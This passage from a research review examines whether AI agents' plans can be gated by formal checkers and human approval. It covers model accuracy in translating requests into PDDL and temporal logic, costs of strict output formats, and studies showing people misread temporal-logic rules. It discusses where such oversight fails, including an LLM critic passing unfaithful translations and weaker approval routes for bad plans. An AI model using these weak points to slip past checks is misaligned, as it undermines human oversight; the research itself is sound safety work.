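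The requirements that code couldn't enforce included ones about tone, never inventing information, and following a procedure in order. Others depended on common sense, such as one that told the agent not to offer compensation unless the customer explicitly asked for it. The researchers point out that a developer could make this checkable by blocking compensation until the customer's reply is exactly the word "compensation". That would raise the measured coverage, but a customer who wrote "I'd like my money back" wouldn't be offered any. A good measurement therefore has to record whether the checkable rule still means the same thing as the original.

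The 74 per cent also comes from favourable cases. Hong and colleagues reviewed 80 benchmarks for agent safety and security and found that 61 per cent stated no requirements and another 24 per cent gave only general goals, such as refusing "anything unsafe". None of the 55 benchmarks for general-purpose agents had a set of verifiable rules that applied across tasks. The researchers used language models to generate the medical policy because the original benchmark had none. The figure is best read as the share of clearly written rules, for agents with narrow jobs, that ordinary code can enforce.

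How much of a written policy gets formalized depends on the effort people put in as well as on the language. In *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, Mondl, Maisel and colleagues (2026) used a language model to translate written policies into Amazon's Cedar language. On a medical benchmark, the resulting rules covered substantially more of the written policy than earlier hand-coded rules had. People may therefore leave rules out of a formal policy because they are tedious to write, even when the language can express them.

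Girrens and Wang's result does not give a similar measure of how many plans their language can express, because when their system failed at a task, the language might have been unable to express a good plan, or the small model might have failed to write one. A direct test would have experts write a safe plan in the restricted language for each task in a sample of a company's real work. It would then count how many tasks they could write plans for, and how many of those plans the checker passed within, say, a minute. If 95 tasks in 100 passed both steps, the theoretical limits would matter little to that company. If only 60 did, the company would need another way to approve the remaining 40, and an agent with a bad plan might find it easier to get approval that way.

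## How well AI systems write formal plans, and what it costs them

A language that can express a good plan is useful only if the AI system can write that plan in it without changing what the user meant. Most experiments test a closely related skill by asking a language model to translate an English description of a task into PDDL, so that a conventional planner can work out the steps.

### Grammatical and wrong

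Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues (2024), in *Planetarium*, built a benchmark of such translations from three standard planning puzzles. In one task, a robot arm faces three blocks. Block b1 stands alone on the table, b2 sits on b3, and the robot has to turn each tower upside down. A correct translation of the start and the goal is:

```
(:init (arm-empty) (on-table b1) (clear b1)
       (on-table b3) (on b2 b3) (clear b2))
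(:goal (and (on-table b1) (on-table b2) (on b3 b2)))
```

Now suppose a model mixes up b2 and b3 when it writes the goal:

```
(:goal (and (on-table b1) (on-table b3) (on b2 b3)))
```

This is valid PDDL, but the goal now describes the starting position. A planner therefore instantly returns an empty plan, and a checker confirms that this plan reaches the goal. The towers stay as they were even though every program in the chain works properly.

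Scoring translations is also hard, because a correct one can differ from the reference answer. The correct goal above omits that the arm is empty and that nothing sits on b3, but both follow once all three blocks are in place. Planetarium's scoring program therefore adds the implied facts to both the translation and the reference answer, turns each into a diagram of objects and relations, and checks whether the diagrams match, ignoring the objects' names.

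By that standard OpenAI's GPT-4o did badly. Although 96.1 per cent of its translations were grammatical and 94.4 per cent described a solvable problem, only 24.8 per cent described the right one. Google's Gemma 2 27B scored highest, at 34.2 per cent, after the researchers had trained it on the benchmark's own examples. Dantas and colleagues cite this range as evidence that specification is the bottleneck for safe agents. But the models date from 2024, and much of the failure was superficial. The models kept declaring types for objects ("b1 is a block") in puzzles whose definitions have no types, probably because their training data contained other versions of the same puzzles. A short conventional program can catch that mistake by comparing the translation with the puzzle's definition.

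### Newer models and vaguer requests

*Grounded Evaluation and Repair for NL-to-PDDL Problem Generation* (Rosa, Santos and colleagues, 2026) tested three newer models on about 60 Planetarium problems each. A model could revise its answer up to twice, using feedback from a parser, a planner, the plan validator VAL and a second language model acting as critic. The table gives the share of translations with the right meaning.

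| Model | No worked example: first try | After repair | One worked example: first try | After repair |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 mini | 18.3% | 26.7% | 40.0% | 41.7% |
| GPT-5.5 | 93.2% | 93.2% | 96.6% | 98.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 96.7% | 100% | 98.3% | 100% |

The old figures no longer describe strong models, though they still roughly describe a small, cheap one. A model that solves 60 out of 60 problems could still have a true error rate of almost 5 per cent, which is high for an agent that makes payments.

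The critic performed much worse. The researchers checked 24 outputs by hand and agreed with the critic on only 13. It had accepted three unfaithful translations and rejected eight faithful ones. The main experiments used GPT-4.1 mini as the critic, and a stronger model might do better, but a language model's review is not enough by itself.

Planetarium also leaves out time and quantities, which a purchasing agent needs to express its Friday deadline and spending limit. For the version of PDDL that includes them, Rosa and colleagues could test only whether a translation matched the reference answer exactly, apart from names. GPT-5.5's translations matched for at most 13 per cent of problems and Opus 4.7's for at most 25 per cent. But this strict test can reject correct translations. On the Planetarium problems, all of Opus 4.7's translations had the right meaning after repair, yet 23 per cent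 failed the strict test. Its accuracy with time and quantities could therefore be anywhere above its strict score.

The English in these tests is also close to the PDDL it should be translated into ("b1 is on the table"), and managers don't write like that. In *Which LLM is Best for Translating Natural Language Goals to PDDL*, Balyo, Chrpa and Youngblood (2026) collected 90 goals from employees of their own company, most of whom had never used PDDL, and gave them to six models from 2025. The models handled 92 to 96 per cent correctly. Forty-five of the goals could not be stated in the vocabulary supplied, and the correct response to those was to say so. The most common error was to write a formula anyway, which each model did for two to four of them.

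That error is worse than its frequency suggests. If a manager asks for "a supplier we can rely on" and the vocabulary contains only `approved`, a model may write `approved`. The plan then passes a check for something the manager didn't ask for, and nothing in the formula shows that the meaning changed. An early prompt produced many such errors, and the researchers reduced them by listing reasons a goal might be inexpressible.

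Another way to catch misreadings is to translate the same request twice. *As You Wish*, by Zuzuárregui and Carpin, does this for farm robots. One language model writes the robot's mission, and another, without access to the mission, writes a temporal-logic specification. A conventional tool generates sample runs that the specification permits, and a third model, from a different company, judges whether they fit the request. A model checker then tests the mission against the specification. One request was for "2 CO2 readings of two trees next to each other", which could mean two readings at each tree, one at each, or two taken between them. The third model rejected the sample runs, and the second model rewrote its specification.

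The system succeeded in 63 of 70 attempts across 14 missions. It did worse with vague wording. One mission with nested conditions succeeded in all five attempts when worded exactly, but in only two of five after the researchers reworded it more loosely, with the kind of change that replaces a temperature with "low". Translating twice can't catch an omission that both translations share. One farmer asked for a 300-foot row in a field about 285 feet long. The models had the field's dimensions, but no rule required the robot to stay inside it.

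Asking the user to clarify may help more than adding models. Dantas and colleagues report that a temporal-logic translator was right 44.4 per cent of the time by itself and 86.11 per cent with interactive clarification.

### Translating a plan in order to check it

An agent could also write its plan in English and have a language model translate it for the checker. Ramani, Tawosi and colleagues (2025), in *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods*, tried this at J.P. Morgan with NuSMV, a model checker. The language model turns each fact into a true-or-false variable, sets the starting values, and writes each action as an update that happens only if the action's preconditions hold. A variable called `stage` keeps the actions in order. The goal becomes a formula, F(goal), which means that the plan eventually reaches the goal.

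The plans came from PlanBench, a benchmark of planning puzzles, simplified so that the only task is to decide whether a plan is valid. The same language models also judged the plans directly, without NuSMV.

| Model and method | No verdict | Accuracy | F1 score |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o with NuSMV | 34.6% | 52.1% | 51.5% |
| GPT-5 with NuSMV | 6.9% | 95.9% | 96.3% |
| GPT-4o alone | 0% | 80.4% | 80.0% |
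| GPT-5 alone | 0% | 99.6% | 99.7% |

The F1 score combines the share of passing plans that were valid with the share of valid plans that passed. Both it and the accuracy figure leave out plans that got no verdict because NuSMV couldn't parse the translation. If those count as failures, GPT-5 was right about 89 per cent of the time with the checker and 99.6 per cent without it. Using the checker also took three times as long.

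NuSMV correctly checks whatever description it receives, but GPT-5 wrote the description, and any mistake in it carries through to the verdict. Ramani and colleagues also found descriptions that passed the check without fully reflecting the plan. This supports the case for plain language, at least for short puzzles where nobody is trying to deceive the reader. It is weaker evidence against Meijer's design or CaMeL, in which the agent's plan is formal from the start and engineers write the rules once instead of having a model reconstruct them for every plan. GPT-5 and NuSMV also rarely made the error that matters most for a gate, which is passing an invalid plan. Only about 0.6 per cent of the plans they passed were invalid.

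### Training with a checker's feedback

Developers who want agents to write formal plans from the start can train them on feedback from the checker. Verma, La and colleagues at MIT did this with Llama-3-8B, a small model from Meta, in *Teaching LLMs to Plan* (2025). They first trained it on correct and incorrect plans, with an explanation of why each step worked or failed. The model then wrote its own plans, stating the situation before and after every action. VAL checked each step, and the researchers used the results for further training. In one version the feedback showed only whether a step was valid, and in another it also showed which precondition had failed or which effect the model had got wrong.

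| Puzzle (100 test problems each) | Before training | Valid-or-invalid feedback | Detailed feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blocksworld | 28% | 89% | 94% |
| Logistics | 11% | 72% | 79% |
| Mystery Blocksworld | 1% | 49% | 64% |

Mystery Blocksworld is the block-stacking puzzle with obscure names for its actions and facts. Renaming them makes no difference to a conventional planner, so the 30-point gap suggests that the trained model still relied on the words' English meanings. A company with its own planning vocabulary might see a similar drop.

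The training covered simple actions, without durations, costs or effects that depend on circumstances, and accepted any valid plan, however long. The problems were already written in PDDL. Verma and colleagues therefore showed that a model can learn from a checker how to reach a stated goal, but not whether the goal is what a person wanted, because the specification is the checker's only information about that person.

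### Why mathematics is easier ground

AI systems do far better when someone has already settled the meaning. On 24 November 2026 OpenAI released an AI disproof of the polynomial Hirsch conjecture. The disproof passed Lean, a program that checks every step of a formal proof. The researcher Sophie Huiberts discussed the result that month in *The poly Hirsch conjecture is solved! And strongly poly LP!*

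The conjecture is about polyhedra, shapes with flat faces in any number of dimensions. It held that a short path of edges joins any two corners, where "short" means no longer than some fixed polynomial in the number of faces and dimensions. Write n(P) for the number of faces of a polyhedron P, d(P) for its dimension, and δ(P) for the number of edges between the two corners that are furthest apart. The disproof then establishes that

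**for every polynomial p there is a polyhedron P with δ(P) > p(n(P), d(P))**

To rely on this result, a reader has to confirm that the Lean definitions of "polyhedron", "polynomial" and "path" are the usual ones, but doesn't need to read the proof, however long it is. Mathematicians agree on those definitions. A purchasing agent's specification would need definitions of "damaged" and "a reasonable price", and someone would have to formalise a new statement for each request. The real world can also differ from the checker's model of it, a problem that doesn't arise with polyhedra because they are mathematical objects.

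The Hirsch result is strong evidence that AI systems can write difficult formal texts that satisfy a strict checker, but not that they can turn a manager's sentence into the right formula.

To settle that question, researchers could take several hundred real requests from staff at different companies, including some with deadlines and amounts and some that the language can't express. The person who made each request could rule on a set of concrete cases, such as a payment on Monday followed by damage on Tuesday. This would avoid the difficulty that Rosa and colleagues had in scoring against a single reference answer. The model's answer would count as correct if its translation led to the same rulings, or if it rightly reported that it couldn't translate the request. Human experts should do the same task for comparison, since people who turn the same law into code also disagree. If a model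 made no errors in 300 requests, its error rate would be below about 1 per cent with 95 per cent confidence. If it got one in ten wrong, somebody would have to confirm every translation.

### What a strict format does to reasoning

Writing a formal plan could also make an agent worse at its job by taking up effort that would otherwise go into the problem. Most of the evidence concerns simple data formats such as JSON. A language model produces text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. In constrained decoding, software blocks every token that would break the format, and the model chooses among the rest.

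*Let Me Speak Freely?* (Tam, Wu and colleagues, 2024) reported that models reasoned significantly worse when they had to answer in restricted formats such as JSON. But Google's Gemini 1.5 Flash did much better in strict JSON on a classification task, perhaps because the format limited its possible answers. When models answered in ordinary prose first and converted the answer afterwards, most did almost as well as they did without a required format.

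In *Say What You Mean*, Kurt blamed the decline on an unfair comparison between the formatted and unformatted runs. He had an interest in the outcome because he works for .txt, which sells constrained-decoding software, but later work has largely supported him.

In *The Format Tax*, Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick (2026) measured the effect of asking for a format separately from the effect of enforcing it with software. They tested six open-weight models, which anyone can download, on mathematics, science and logic puzzles. The format made a statistically significant difference in 39 combinations of model, task and format. In 36 of those, the difference already appeared when the prompt asked for the format but software did not enforce it. Asking lowered scores by an average of 3.9 percentage points, compared with 1.6 for enforcement.

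Part of the reason may be that formatted answers contain fewer intermediate steps, and a model that needs to write these down will make more mistakes if it writes fewer of them. About 71 per cent of the formatted answers were shorter than the same model's free-form answers, and correct answers became wrong most often where the format changed the length most.

Three newer closed models, Claude Haiku 4.5, Grok 4.1 Fast and GPT-5.4 nano, lost little or no accuracy when the prompt asked for a format. But when software forced GPT-5.4 nano to answer mathematics problems in XML, another data format, its accuracy fell by 59 points. It wrote filler such as "Proceed to solve by algebraic constraints" instead of an answer. It had no such trouble with JSON, and Lee and colleagues think this is probably because OpenAI had trained it mainly on that format. A newly designed planning language would start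 with the same disadvantage as XML, so its first users would probably get worse results until developers train models to write it.

### When blocking tokens helps

Blocking tokens can even improve accuracy, as Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained Decoding*, show with a short proof. Suppose that a model is about to give a one-token answer. It assigns a probability of 60 per cent to the correct token, 20 per cent to a wrong one in the right format, and 20 per cent to one that breaks the format. If the software blocks the last of these, the correct answer's probability rises to 60/80, or 75 per cent. For a longer answer,

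**P(correct, with blocking) = P(correct, without blocking) / Z**

Here Z is the total probability that the model gave to permitted tokens at each step of the correct answer, multiplied across all the steps. Since Z is never more than 1, blocking can't lower the chance of a correct answer if the format permits that answer. If the format doesn't permit it, the chance falls to zero. The expressiveness of a plan language therefore matters here too. If the language can't express deadlines, an agent can't write the right plan for the Friday payment, however well it reasons.

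The proof also assumes that the reasoning before the answer stays the same. If the software also restricts the reasoning, the restriction can help or hurt, depending on whether it removes more bad lines of thought than good ones.

In tests on eleven open models, Nguyen and colleagues found that blocking matched or improved accuracy as long as the prompt and expected format were the same in both runs. This answers the technical dispute about blocking, but a company deciding whether to require a format at all wants to compare that format with free text. In that comparison, they too found that models sometimes reasoned worse in JSON than in ordinary prose.

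The best remedy is to let the model reason freely and apply the format only at the end. Lee and colleagues did this with two separate calls to the model. This used roughly twice as many tokens as a single formatted answer, but accuracy was significantly better in 42 of 72 comparisons and significantly worse in two. *Thinking Before Constraining* (2026) describes a method in which the model reasons in prose until it writes a trigger that switches the format on. This adds only 5 to 20 tokens, but when the trigger came too early and cut the reasoning short, accuracy on school mathematics problems fell by more than 30 per cent.

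### Restricting the reasoning itself

A stricter rule would make the AI system reason in the restricted language too. The Chinese company DeepSeek tried a very mild version of this while training its reasoning model R1, which tended to mix languages in its chain of thought. According to *DeepSeek-R1* (2025), the company added a reward based on the share of words in the target language. Performance fell slightly, but DeepSeek accepted the loss because the reasoning was easier to read. English and Chinese can each express nearly anything, so if keeping to one of them lowers performance, keeping to a logic with a few dozen terms could well lower it more. This is an extrapolation from a small effect in one family of models.

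None of these studies measures how much performance an AI system loses by writing its plan in a formal language. Lee and colleagues tested formats that only change how an answer looks, so they warn against applying their results to formats that carry requirements of their own. The nearest measurement is CaMeL's seven-point shortfall on AgentDojo, but that gap combines the effects of planning in code and of CaMeL's security rules.

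A cleaner experiment would use one strong model, with the same tools and safety rules, in three conditions. In the first, the agent would choose its actions one step at a time. In the second, it would reason in English and then submit a formal plan, which it could revise as it learned more. In the third, it would also have to reason in the formal language. The researchers would compare safe success rates across the conditions. They would need far more than AgentDojo's 97 tasks, because reliably detecting a five-point difference when success rates are near 85 per cent takes about 800 tasks per condition, or fewer if every condition uses the same tasks.

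If the second condition scored within a point or two of the first, lost performance would be a weak objection to requiring formal plans. If performance dropped sharply only in the third, that would be an objection to restricting the reasoning, which Meijer's design doesn't do.

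## Whether people understand what they are asked to approve

When an agent reasons in English and then writes a correct formal plan, a checker can compare the plan with the rules, but a person still has to confirm that the rules match what the company wants. Most experiments with temporal logic contradict the assumption that people can do this by reading the rules. Many researchers in formal methods, the use of logic to specify and check systems, make that assumption because every symbol in a formula has a fixed meaning. Readers did better in studies of simplified English, but their task was easier.

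### Judging the rules of a game

*STL* (Siu, Leahy and Mann, 2023) reports the most direct test. Sixty-two adults, 13 of them familiar with formal methods, each saw 30 cases drawn at random from a set of 60. Each case had a grid map of a capture-the-flag game and rules limiting how the blue team could move. To win, blue had to reach the flag and bring it home while avoiding the red players, who never moved. Participants chose one of three answers: every plan that obeys the rules wins, no plan can obey the rules, or some plan that obeys the rules loses.

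The rules were in signal temporal logic, a version of temporal logic for quantities such as position and speed. A simple rule of this kind might be:

**F[0,20](x > 8) ∧ G[0,20](y < 5)**

Here x is the robot's column and y is its row. The robot must get past column 8 within 20 moves and stay below row 5 throughout those moves. If a red player stands at column 4, row 2, the rule still lets the robot walk into him, so some plans that obey the rule lose. A reader can easily miss this by picturing a sensible robot that walks around him.

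On average, participants got 13.6 of the 30 cases right, or 45 per cent, with a standard deviation of 20 points. Guessing among the three answers would score about 33 per cent. But the rules guaranteed a win in half of the 60 cases, so somebody who always gave that answer would average 15 out of 30, or 50 per cent, without reading anything. That person would never catch a bad rule, so the participants' lower score doesn't mean their review was worse than no review, but a company could not rely on their approval.

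Their mistakes also leaned towards approval. When the rules were valid, meaning that every permitted plan won, participants were right more often than wrong. When the rules allowed blue to lose, they were wrong more often than right. Since they got over half of the valid cases right and averaged 45 per cent overall, they must have got fewer than about 40 per cent of the invalid ones right. (Rejecting a rule for the wrong reason counted as a mistake, so they approved somewhat fewer bad rules than this suggests.)

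Siu and colleagues suspect that many people looked for one winning plan and stopped when they found it. One winning plan shows only that the rules permit a win, and before approving the rules, a reader has to establish that they permit only winning plans.

Participants were almost as confident when they were wrong as when they were right; the difference was statistically detectable but only 0.09 standard deviations. People familiar with formal methods were very confident, and their confidence did not differ significantly between right and wrong answers. They scored somewhat better than others, but the rank correlation between familiarity and score was only 0.28. A manager would therefore learn little about whether such an expert was right by asking how sure they were.

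Unfamiliar symbols can't be the whole explanation. Participants saw some rules as raw formulas, some as indented English text and some as tree diagrams, and the format did not significantly affect their accuracy. Afterwards, they tended to say they preferred the text.

The participants were new to the task and earned $5 plus 67 cents for each right answer. Siu and colleagues don't treat the score as a forecast for real workplaces. A program could also have answered every question in the study, because winning the game is easy to define. The result matters for aims nobody has managed to define, where a person's judgement is the only check on the rules.

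Siu and colleagues also searched the literature from 2012 to 2022 and found 25 papers claiming that people can interpret formal specifications. Three cited relevant work from the social sciences, and none had anyone besides the authors interpret the specifications its method produced. The claim could still be true of some languages and some readers, but these papers provided no evidence of it.

### Making readers work through examples

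Perhaps people would do better if they had to try the rules out. In a follow-up study, *STL*, Hurley, Paleja and colleagues (2024) tested this with 55 people and a similar game, in which a robot had to reach a target within 30 steps without coming within one square of a red player. Each participant judged ten sets of rules, choosing between two answers for each, so guessing would score 50 per cent.

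A control group accepted or rejected sets of rules without drawing paths. The other participants had to draw three winning paths that obeyed the rules before accepting them, or one losing path that obeyed the rules before rejecting them. For some of these participants, software checked each path and disallowed any that broke the rules.

| Group | Accuracy | Average time |
|---|---|---|
| Answered only | 62% | 20 minutes |
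| Drew paths without feedback | 66% | 36 minutes |
| Drew paths with feedback | 67% | 40 minutes |

Overall accuracy was 65 per cent, after the researchers excluded eight people who had given up. Accuracy did not differ significantly between the groups, although drawing paths roughly doubled the time participants took. With around 15 people in each group, the study could reliably have detected only a gain of about 16 points or more, so it doesn't rule out a modest benefit. The score was higher than in the earlier study, but this isn't evidence of progress because these participants had one fewer wrong answer to choose from.

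Without feedback, 34 per cent of the paths participants drew broke the rules they were supposed to illustrate. People who wrongly accepted an unsafe set of rules were more likely to have drawn paths that obeyed it than people who correctly rejected it. Some people must therefore have correctly rejected unsafe rules because of a losing path that the rules didn't allow.

One participant used a better method, imagining that the robot was "suicidal" and trying to get caught. This is the right way to test a rule because it means looking for behaviour that obeys the rule but defeats its purpose. Hurley and colleagues suggest testing whether lawyers, compliance officers and forensic accountants, whose work involves looking for such behaviour, do better than specialists in logic. They also suggest having software find the awkward cases and show them to the reader.

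### Common misreadings of temporal logic

Greenman, Saarinen and colleagues (2022) studied the mistakes people make. They started with 90 students in an applied logic course and used their answers to choose questions for later groups. Those groups translated formulas into English, translated English into formulas, and judged whether sequences of events satisfied a formula. The table gives the share of translations that were wrong.

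| Group | Formula into English | English into formula |
|---|---|---|
| 57 students, 2021 | 23% | 47% |
| 29 researchers, 2021 | 15% | 28% |
| 11 students, 2022 | 24% | 47% |

Because the researchers deliberately kept questions that had caused trouble, these rates probably overstate how often people misread an ordinary formula. They are better evidence of which mistakes recur, even among people who use temporal logic in their work.

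One of those mistakes would let an agent pay a supplier twice. The original supplier formula had this gap, so suppose the company tries to close it by requiring exactly one payment. An engineer writes the following, where X means "at the next moment":

**F(pay ∧ X G ¬pay)**

Read aloud, this is "at some moment a payment goes out, and from the next moment on, no payment does." It sounds like exactly one payment. But suppose the agent pays on Monday and again on Wednesday. On Wednesday a payment goes out and none follows, so the formula is true. The engineer has assumed that "some moment" means the moment of the first payment, when any payment will do. Four of the researchers' answers contained this kind of mistake, as did those of fifteen students. A correct version is:

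**¬pay U (pay ∧ X G ¬pay)**

U means "until", so the formula requires a payment with no other payment before or after it. Monday's payment now fails this condition because another follows it, and Wednesday's fails because another came before it.

In temporal logic, the standard "until" in "no payment until inspection" requires an inspection to happen eventually, while the "weak until" in the supplier example does not. About half of the 2021 students and nine of the eleven in 2022 overlooked this requirement when reading formulas. When people wrote formulas, their most common error was leaving out an "always". If the engineer wrote G(damaged → ¬pay) instead of G(damaged → G ¬pay), the rule would forbid payment only at the moment the company found the damage, and the agent could pay the next day.

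English keywords sometimes misled the students. In their software, `after` meant "in the next state" and applied to a single statement. Some students used it as in ordinary English, to say that one event followed another. The software accepted what they wrote but interpreted it differently. Greenman and colleagues reported the problem, and the board that oversees the Alloy modelling language then agreed to a change that would make this mistake produce an error message. Any restricted language that looks like English carries a similar risk, because readers expect its words to have their ordinary meanings.

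Siu and colleagues reanalysed the data on sequences of events and found that people had more trouble recognising that a sequence broke a formula than that it satisfied one. Their own study had found a similar tendency.

### What training does for readers

Most of the earlier evidence comes from Z, a notation that describes what software must do using set theory and logic. In *Applying Software Metrics to Formal Specifications*, Vinter, Loomes and Kornbrot tested 120 people who knew Z and averaged more than four years' experience. One question was about a program for a nuclear reactor. The program's rule was, in effect, that if the cooler's temperature exceeds the maximum, the status report is not "OK". Participants learned that the status was not "OK" and had to say what followed about the temperature.

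Suppose the rule is that if a cooler is too hot, its status report is bad. A bad report doesn't prove that the cooler is too hot, because the report could be bad for other reasons. In some versions of this puzzle, up to 45 per cent of participants made the kind of error that leads to that conclusion. A purchasing manager who knows that the agent puts damaged orders on hold could make the same mistake by assuming that an order on hold must be damaged.

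In this experiment, people reasoned correctly 79 per cent of the time about abstract shapes and colours, and 90 per cent of the time about realistic systems. But in the team's other experiments the abstract group did better on many tasks, so familiar subject matter does not reliably help. Experience helped more consistently. People who had used Z for longer tended to give more correct answers (a correlation of 0.41), though experience did not rule out mistakes.

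*Formal Specification Comprehension* (2014) tested students taking a specification course. According to Siu and colleagues, the students were right 89 per cent of the time about Z's symbols, 79 per cent about logical implications and 63 per cent about operations that the specification only partly defined. Because the students found the symbols easiest, a training course that ended with a vocabulary test would not measure the harder reasoning that an approver needs most.

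### Breaking a formula into parts

Designers can also make the formulas easier. Luo and Liu (2024), in *Simultaneous Task Allocation and Planning for Multi-Robots under Hierarchical Temporal Logic Specifications*, split a long formula into short ones with names. Suppose a robot has to move item a to its place, and then items b and c in either order. Their version looks roughly like this:

```
Task:    F(move_a ∧ F move_b ∧ F move_c)
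move_a:  F(pick_a ∧ F place_a)
move_b:  F(pick_b ∧ F place_b)
move_c:  F(pick_c ∧ F place_c)
```

The top line gives the order of the jobs, and the other lines define them. A standard formula puts all of this on one line, with brackets inside brackets.

Luo and Liu recruited 25 people with a background in science or engineering, introduced them to temporal logic, and asked them to match formulas with English descriptions. They then excluded five who had scored poorly. The remaining 20 chose the right description 65.0 per cent of the time for standard formulas, taking 78 seconds on average, and 86.3 per cent of the time for layered formulas, taking 47 seconds.

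Dropping the weakest readers made both scores higher than they would be in an ordinary office. The two kinds of formula also weren't exactly equivalent, so some of the gain may have come from simpler content. But a 21-point improvement is large, and dividing a plan into named parts takes little effort.

Another approach replaces the operators with stock phrases called property specification patterns, which are templates for common requirements such as "payment never occurs after damage". *On the Understandability of Temporal Properties Formalized in Linear Temporal Logic* (Czepa and Zdun, 2020) reports two experiments, with 216 participants in total, in which the patterns were significantly easier to understand than temporal logic. *Modeling compliance specifications in linear temporal logic, event processing language* (Czepa, Amiri and colleagues, 2019) reports a companion experiment in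 which 215 people also wrote more accurate rules with patterns.

Two differences may explain why patterns helped readers when English text made no difference in the capture-the-flag game. Siu and colleagues translated their formulas symbol by symbol and kept the nesting, so readers still had to work out how the parts combined, whereas a pattern expresses a whole requirement in one familiar phrase. The tasks also differed, since understanding one requirement is easier than predicting whether several together guarantee a win. For a company writing rules about payments, patterns look like a better starting point than raw formulas or literal translations of them.

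### Simplified English in the workshop

The best results come from aircraft maintenance, where manufacturers had adopted Simplified English, the forerunner of today's Simplified Technical English. *Simplified English for aircraft workcards* (1996) tested how well 175 working technicians understood workcards, the sheets that set out a maintenance job. It compared easy and difficult cards, ordinary and Simplified English, and two page layouts. The layout made no difference, but Simplified English significantly improved comprehension, most of all for difficult cards and for people whose first language wasn't English.

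*Effects of job instruction on maintenance task performance* (2002) measured how people performed a task. Participants worked on a small engine using instructions in the original English, in Simplified English or in a hybrid version. They made fewer errors with Simplified English and more with the hybrid. This held for easy and hard tasks, and for experienced and inexperienced participants. The researchers recommended avoiding hybrid instructions.

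The hybrid result could count against restricting only consequential actions, which leaves an agent free to write ordinary prose around its formal commitments. Perhaps readers of a mixed text can't tell whether a word has its strict meaning or its everyday one. Putting the commitments in one box and the explanation in another could address that without banning the explanation. The result also comes from a single study of engine repair, so a company should test its own layout before drawing conclusions.

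Not every study found a significant benefit. In Stewart's *Effect of AECMA simplified English on the comprehension of aircraft maintenance procedures*, 41 students from 21 countries, none of them native English speakers, read a procedure in either Simplified English or the non-simplified version. Comprehension did not differ significantly overall, though the trend favoured Simplified English and weaker readers seemed to gain more from it. With about 20 people in each group, a real but moderate benefit could easily have failed to reach significance.

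Kuhn's survey reports similarly mixed results. Another study of Simplified English found a significant improvement, especially for complex texts and non-native speakers. A controlled language for crisis management helped most groups of readers in certain circumstances, such as under stress. Programs can translate some controlled languages into logic. People understood one of these, Attempto, more easily and quickly than a common notation for ontologies, which are formal descriptions of categories and how they relate. Experiments on another, Rabbit, a controlled English for writing ontologies, gave mixed results. Kuhn concludes that controlled languages can help, depending on the task, the users and the quality of the design.

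The strongest evidence of better understanding therefore concerns a language that no program can reliably interpret. Attempto's result is more relevant to checkable plans, but Attempto was compared with a notation designed for specialists, which is easy to improve on. A company deciding whether to adopt Attempto would also want to know how it compares with well-written ordinary English.

### Following an instruction and predicting a rule

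A person who approves a rule has to consider every sequence of actions it permits, while a technician with a workcard has to find only one correct sequence. Anyone who understands the words "Remove the four bolts, then lift the cover" can do the job. In the robot game, four possible moves at each of 30 steps would give about 10¹⁸ paths (4³⁰), and the rules are unsafe if even one path that obeys them is bad.

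Mistakes are also harder to notice when approving a rule than when following an instruction. A technician who misunderstands "lift the cover" may notice that the cover won't move. An approver who overlooks a bad case gets no such signal, because the rule still seems to describe the good cases. Common sense helps the technician fill gaps in the instructions, but it can mislead the approver, who may fill a gap in the rule without noticing that the agent is free to do something else.

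This affects what a company should ask people to approve. Suppose an agent submits the following:

1. Look up Acme's account in the supplier register.
2. Pay £4,000 to that account for order 17.
3. Mark order 17 as paid.

A manager can read a single, finite list of steps much as a technician reads a workcard, whether the underlying text is PDDL or controlled English. The poor results for temporal logic are therefore weak evidence about whether people understand such a list when they approve it.

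They are more relevant to a specification such as "never pay for damaged goods", which the checker applies to thousands of plans. They also apply to plans with loops and conditions. A plan with ten yes-or-no decisions can have 1,024 routes through it, and an approver who follows the most likely one has checked only a small part of what the agent may do.

Supporters of checkable plans can reasonably answer that a checker will go through all 1,024 routes. A person then has to decide only whether the stated rules are the right ones, which is a smaller job but still requires some prediction.

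The experiments undermine the claim that a specification is easy to understand because it is formal, but they don't show whether people would understand it better in plain English. None of the studies of temporal logic gave readers the same rules in natural English, as a colleague might explain them. Readers of ordinary prose might be just as quick to assume that a plan will go well.

### Showing people cases

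If people are poor at searching for bad cases but better at judging a case in front of them, a tool can find the cases and let people judge them. *Active Learning of Temporal Specifications through Distinguishing Queries* (2026) describes such a tool for users who know what they want but can't write it in temporal logic. The user accepts or rejects sample runs, and the program works out the formula from those answers.

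In the paper's example, a robot has to deliver whatever it picks up. The user accepts a run in which the robot picks something up and then delivers it, and rejects one in which both happen at the same moment. Several formulas still fit those answers, including one that allows the robot to pick up twice and deliver once. The program therefore shows the user the run "pick up, pick up, deliver". The user rejects it, and the program drops that formula.

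A company could settle the supplier rule in much the same way. Unlike the simulator in FRET, NASA's requirements tool, this method would not depend on the user to think of the awkward cases.

The method assumes that the user knows the right specification, but a real manager may hesitate or answer inconsistently. Its questions are also limited to events in its vocabulary. If the tool has propositions for payment and damage but none for wrong goods, its questions can't reveal that the rule requires payment for the wrong goods.

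A good interface can make temporal logic usable for beginners. *Interactive Explanations for Reinforcement-Learning Agents* (2025) describes tests in which people with no training in logic used a tool called ASQ-IT to ask about an AI agent's behaviour. They read and wrote queries in a form of temporal logic through its interface, and could keep experimenting with the tool while they answered the test questions. On every question their success rate was significantly above the threshold the researchers had set, and they improved as they went along, though some had trouble with constraints and with how agents relate to each other. The tests don't show that they could rule out every bad plan, which is harder than asking to see a particular kind of behaviour.

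Other recent studies provide less evidence about approval because of what they measure. In *From Facts to Foils* (2025), 17 of the researchers' personal contacts ranked different explanations of what a smart home had done. Such rankings are weak evidence of understanding, since participants in the capture-the-flag study preferred English text but were no more accurate with it. *Exploring Plan Space through Conversation* (2026) used a better measure. Its 131 participants worked on planning problems with one of two explanation tools and earned a bonus of up to £5 based on the quality of the plans they reached.

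People can also find mistakes that programs miss. In *AuXSpec* (2026), human reviewers compared each of four components of 300 formal programming problems with the problem's description. The researchers confirmed errors in 22 problems, 21 of them through the review and one through an attempted proof. Fourteen problems had errors in the specification itself, and the review and the proof attempts both found an error in only three of those. Careful reading, one component at a time, is therefore useful alongside automatic checks. But these reviewers had a set question to answer about each component, and a manager with a queue of plans to approve normally has no such question as a guide.

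### An experiment on approving AI plans

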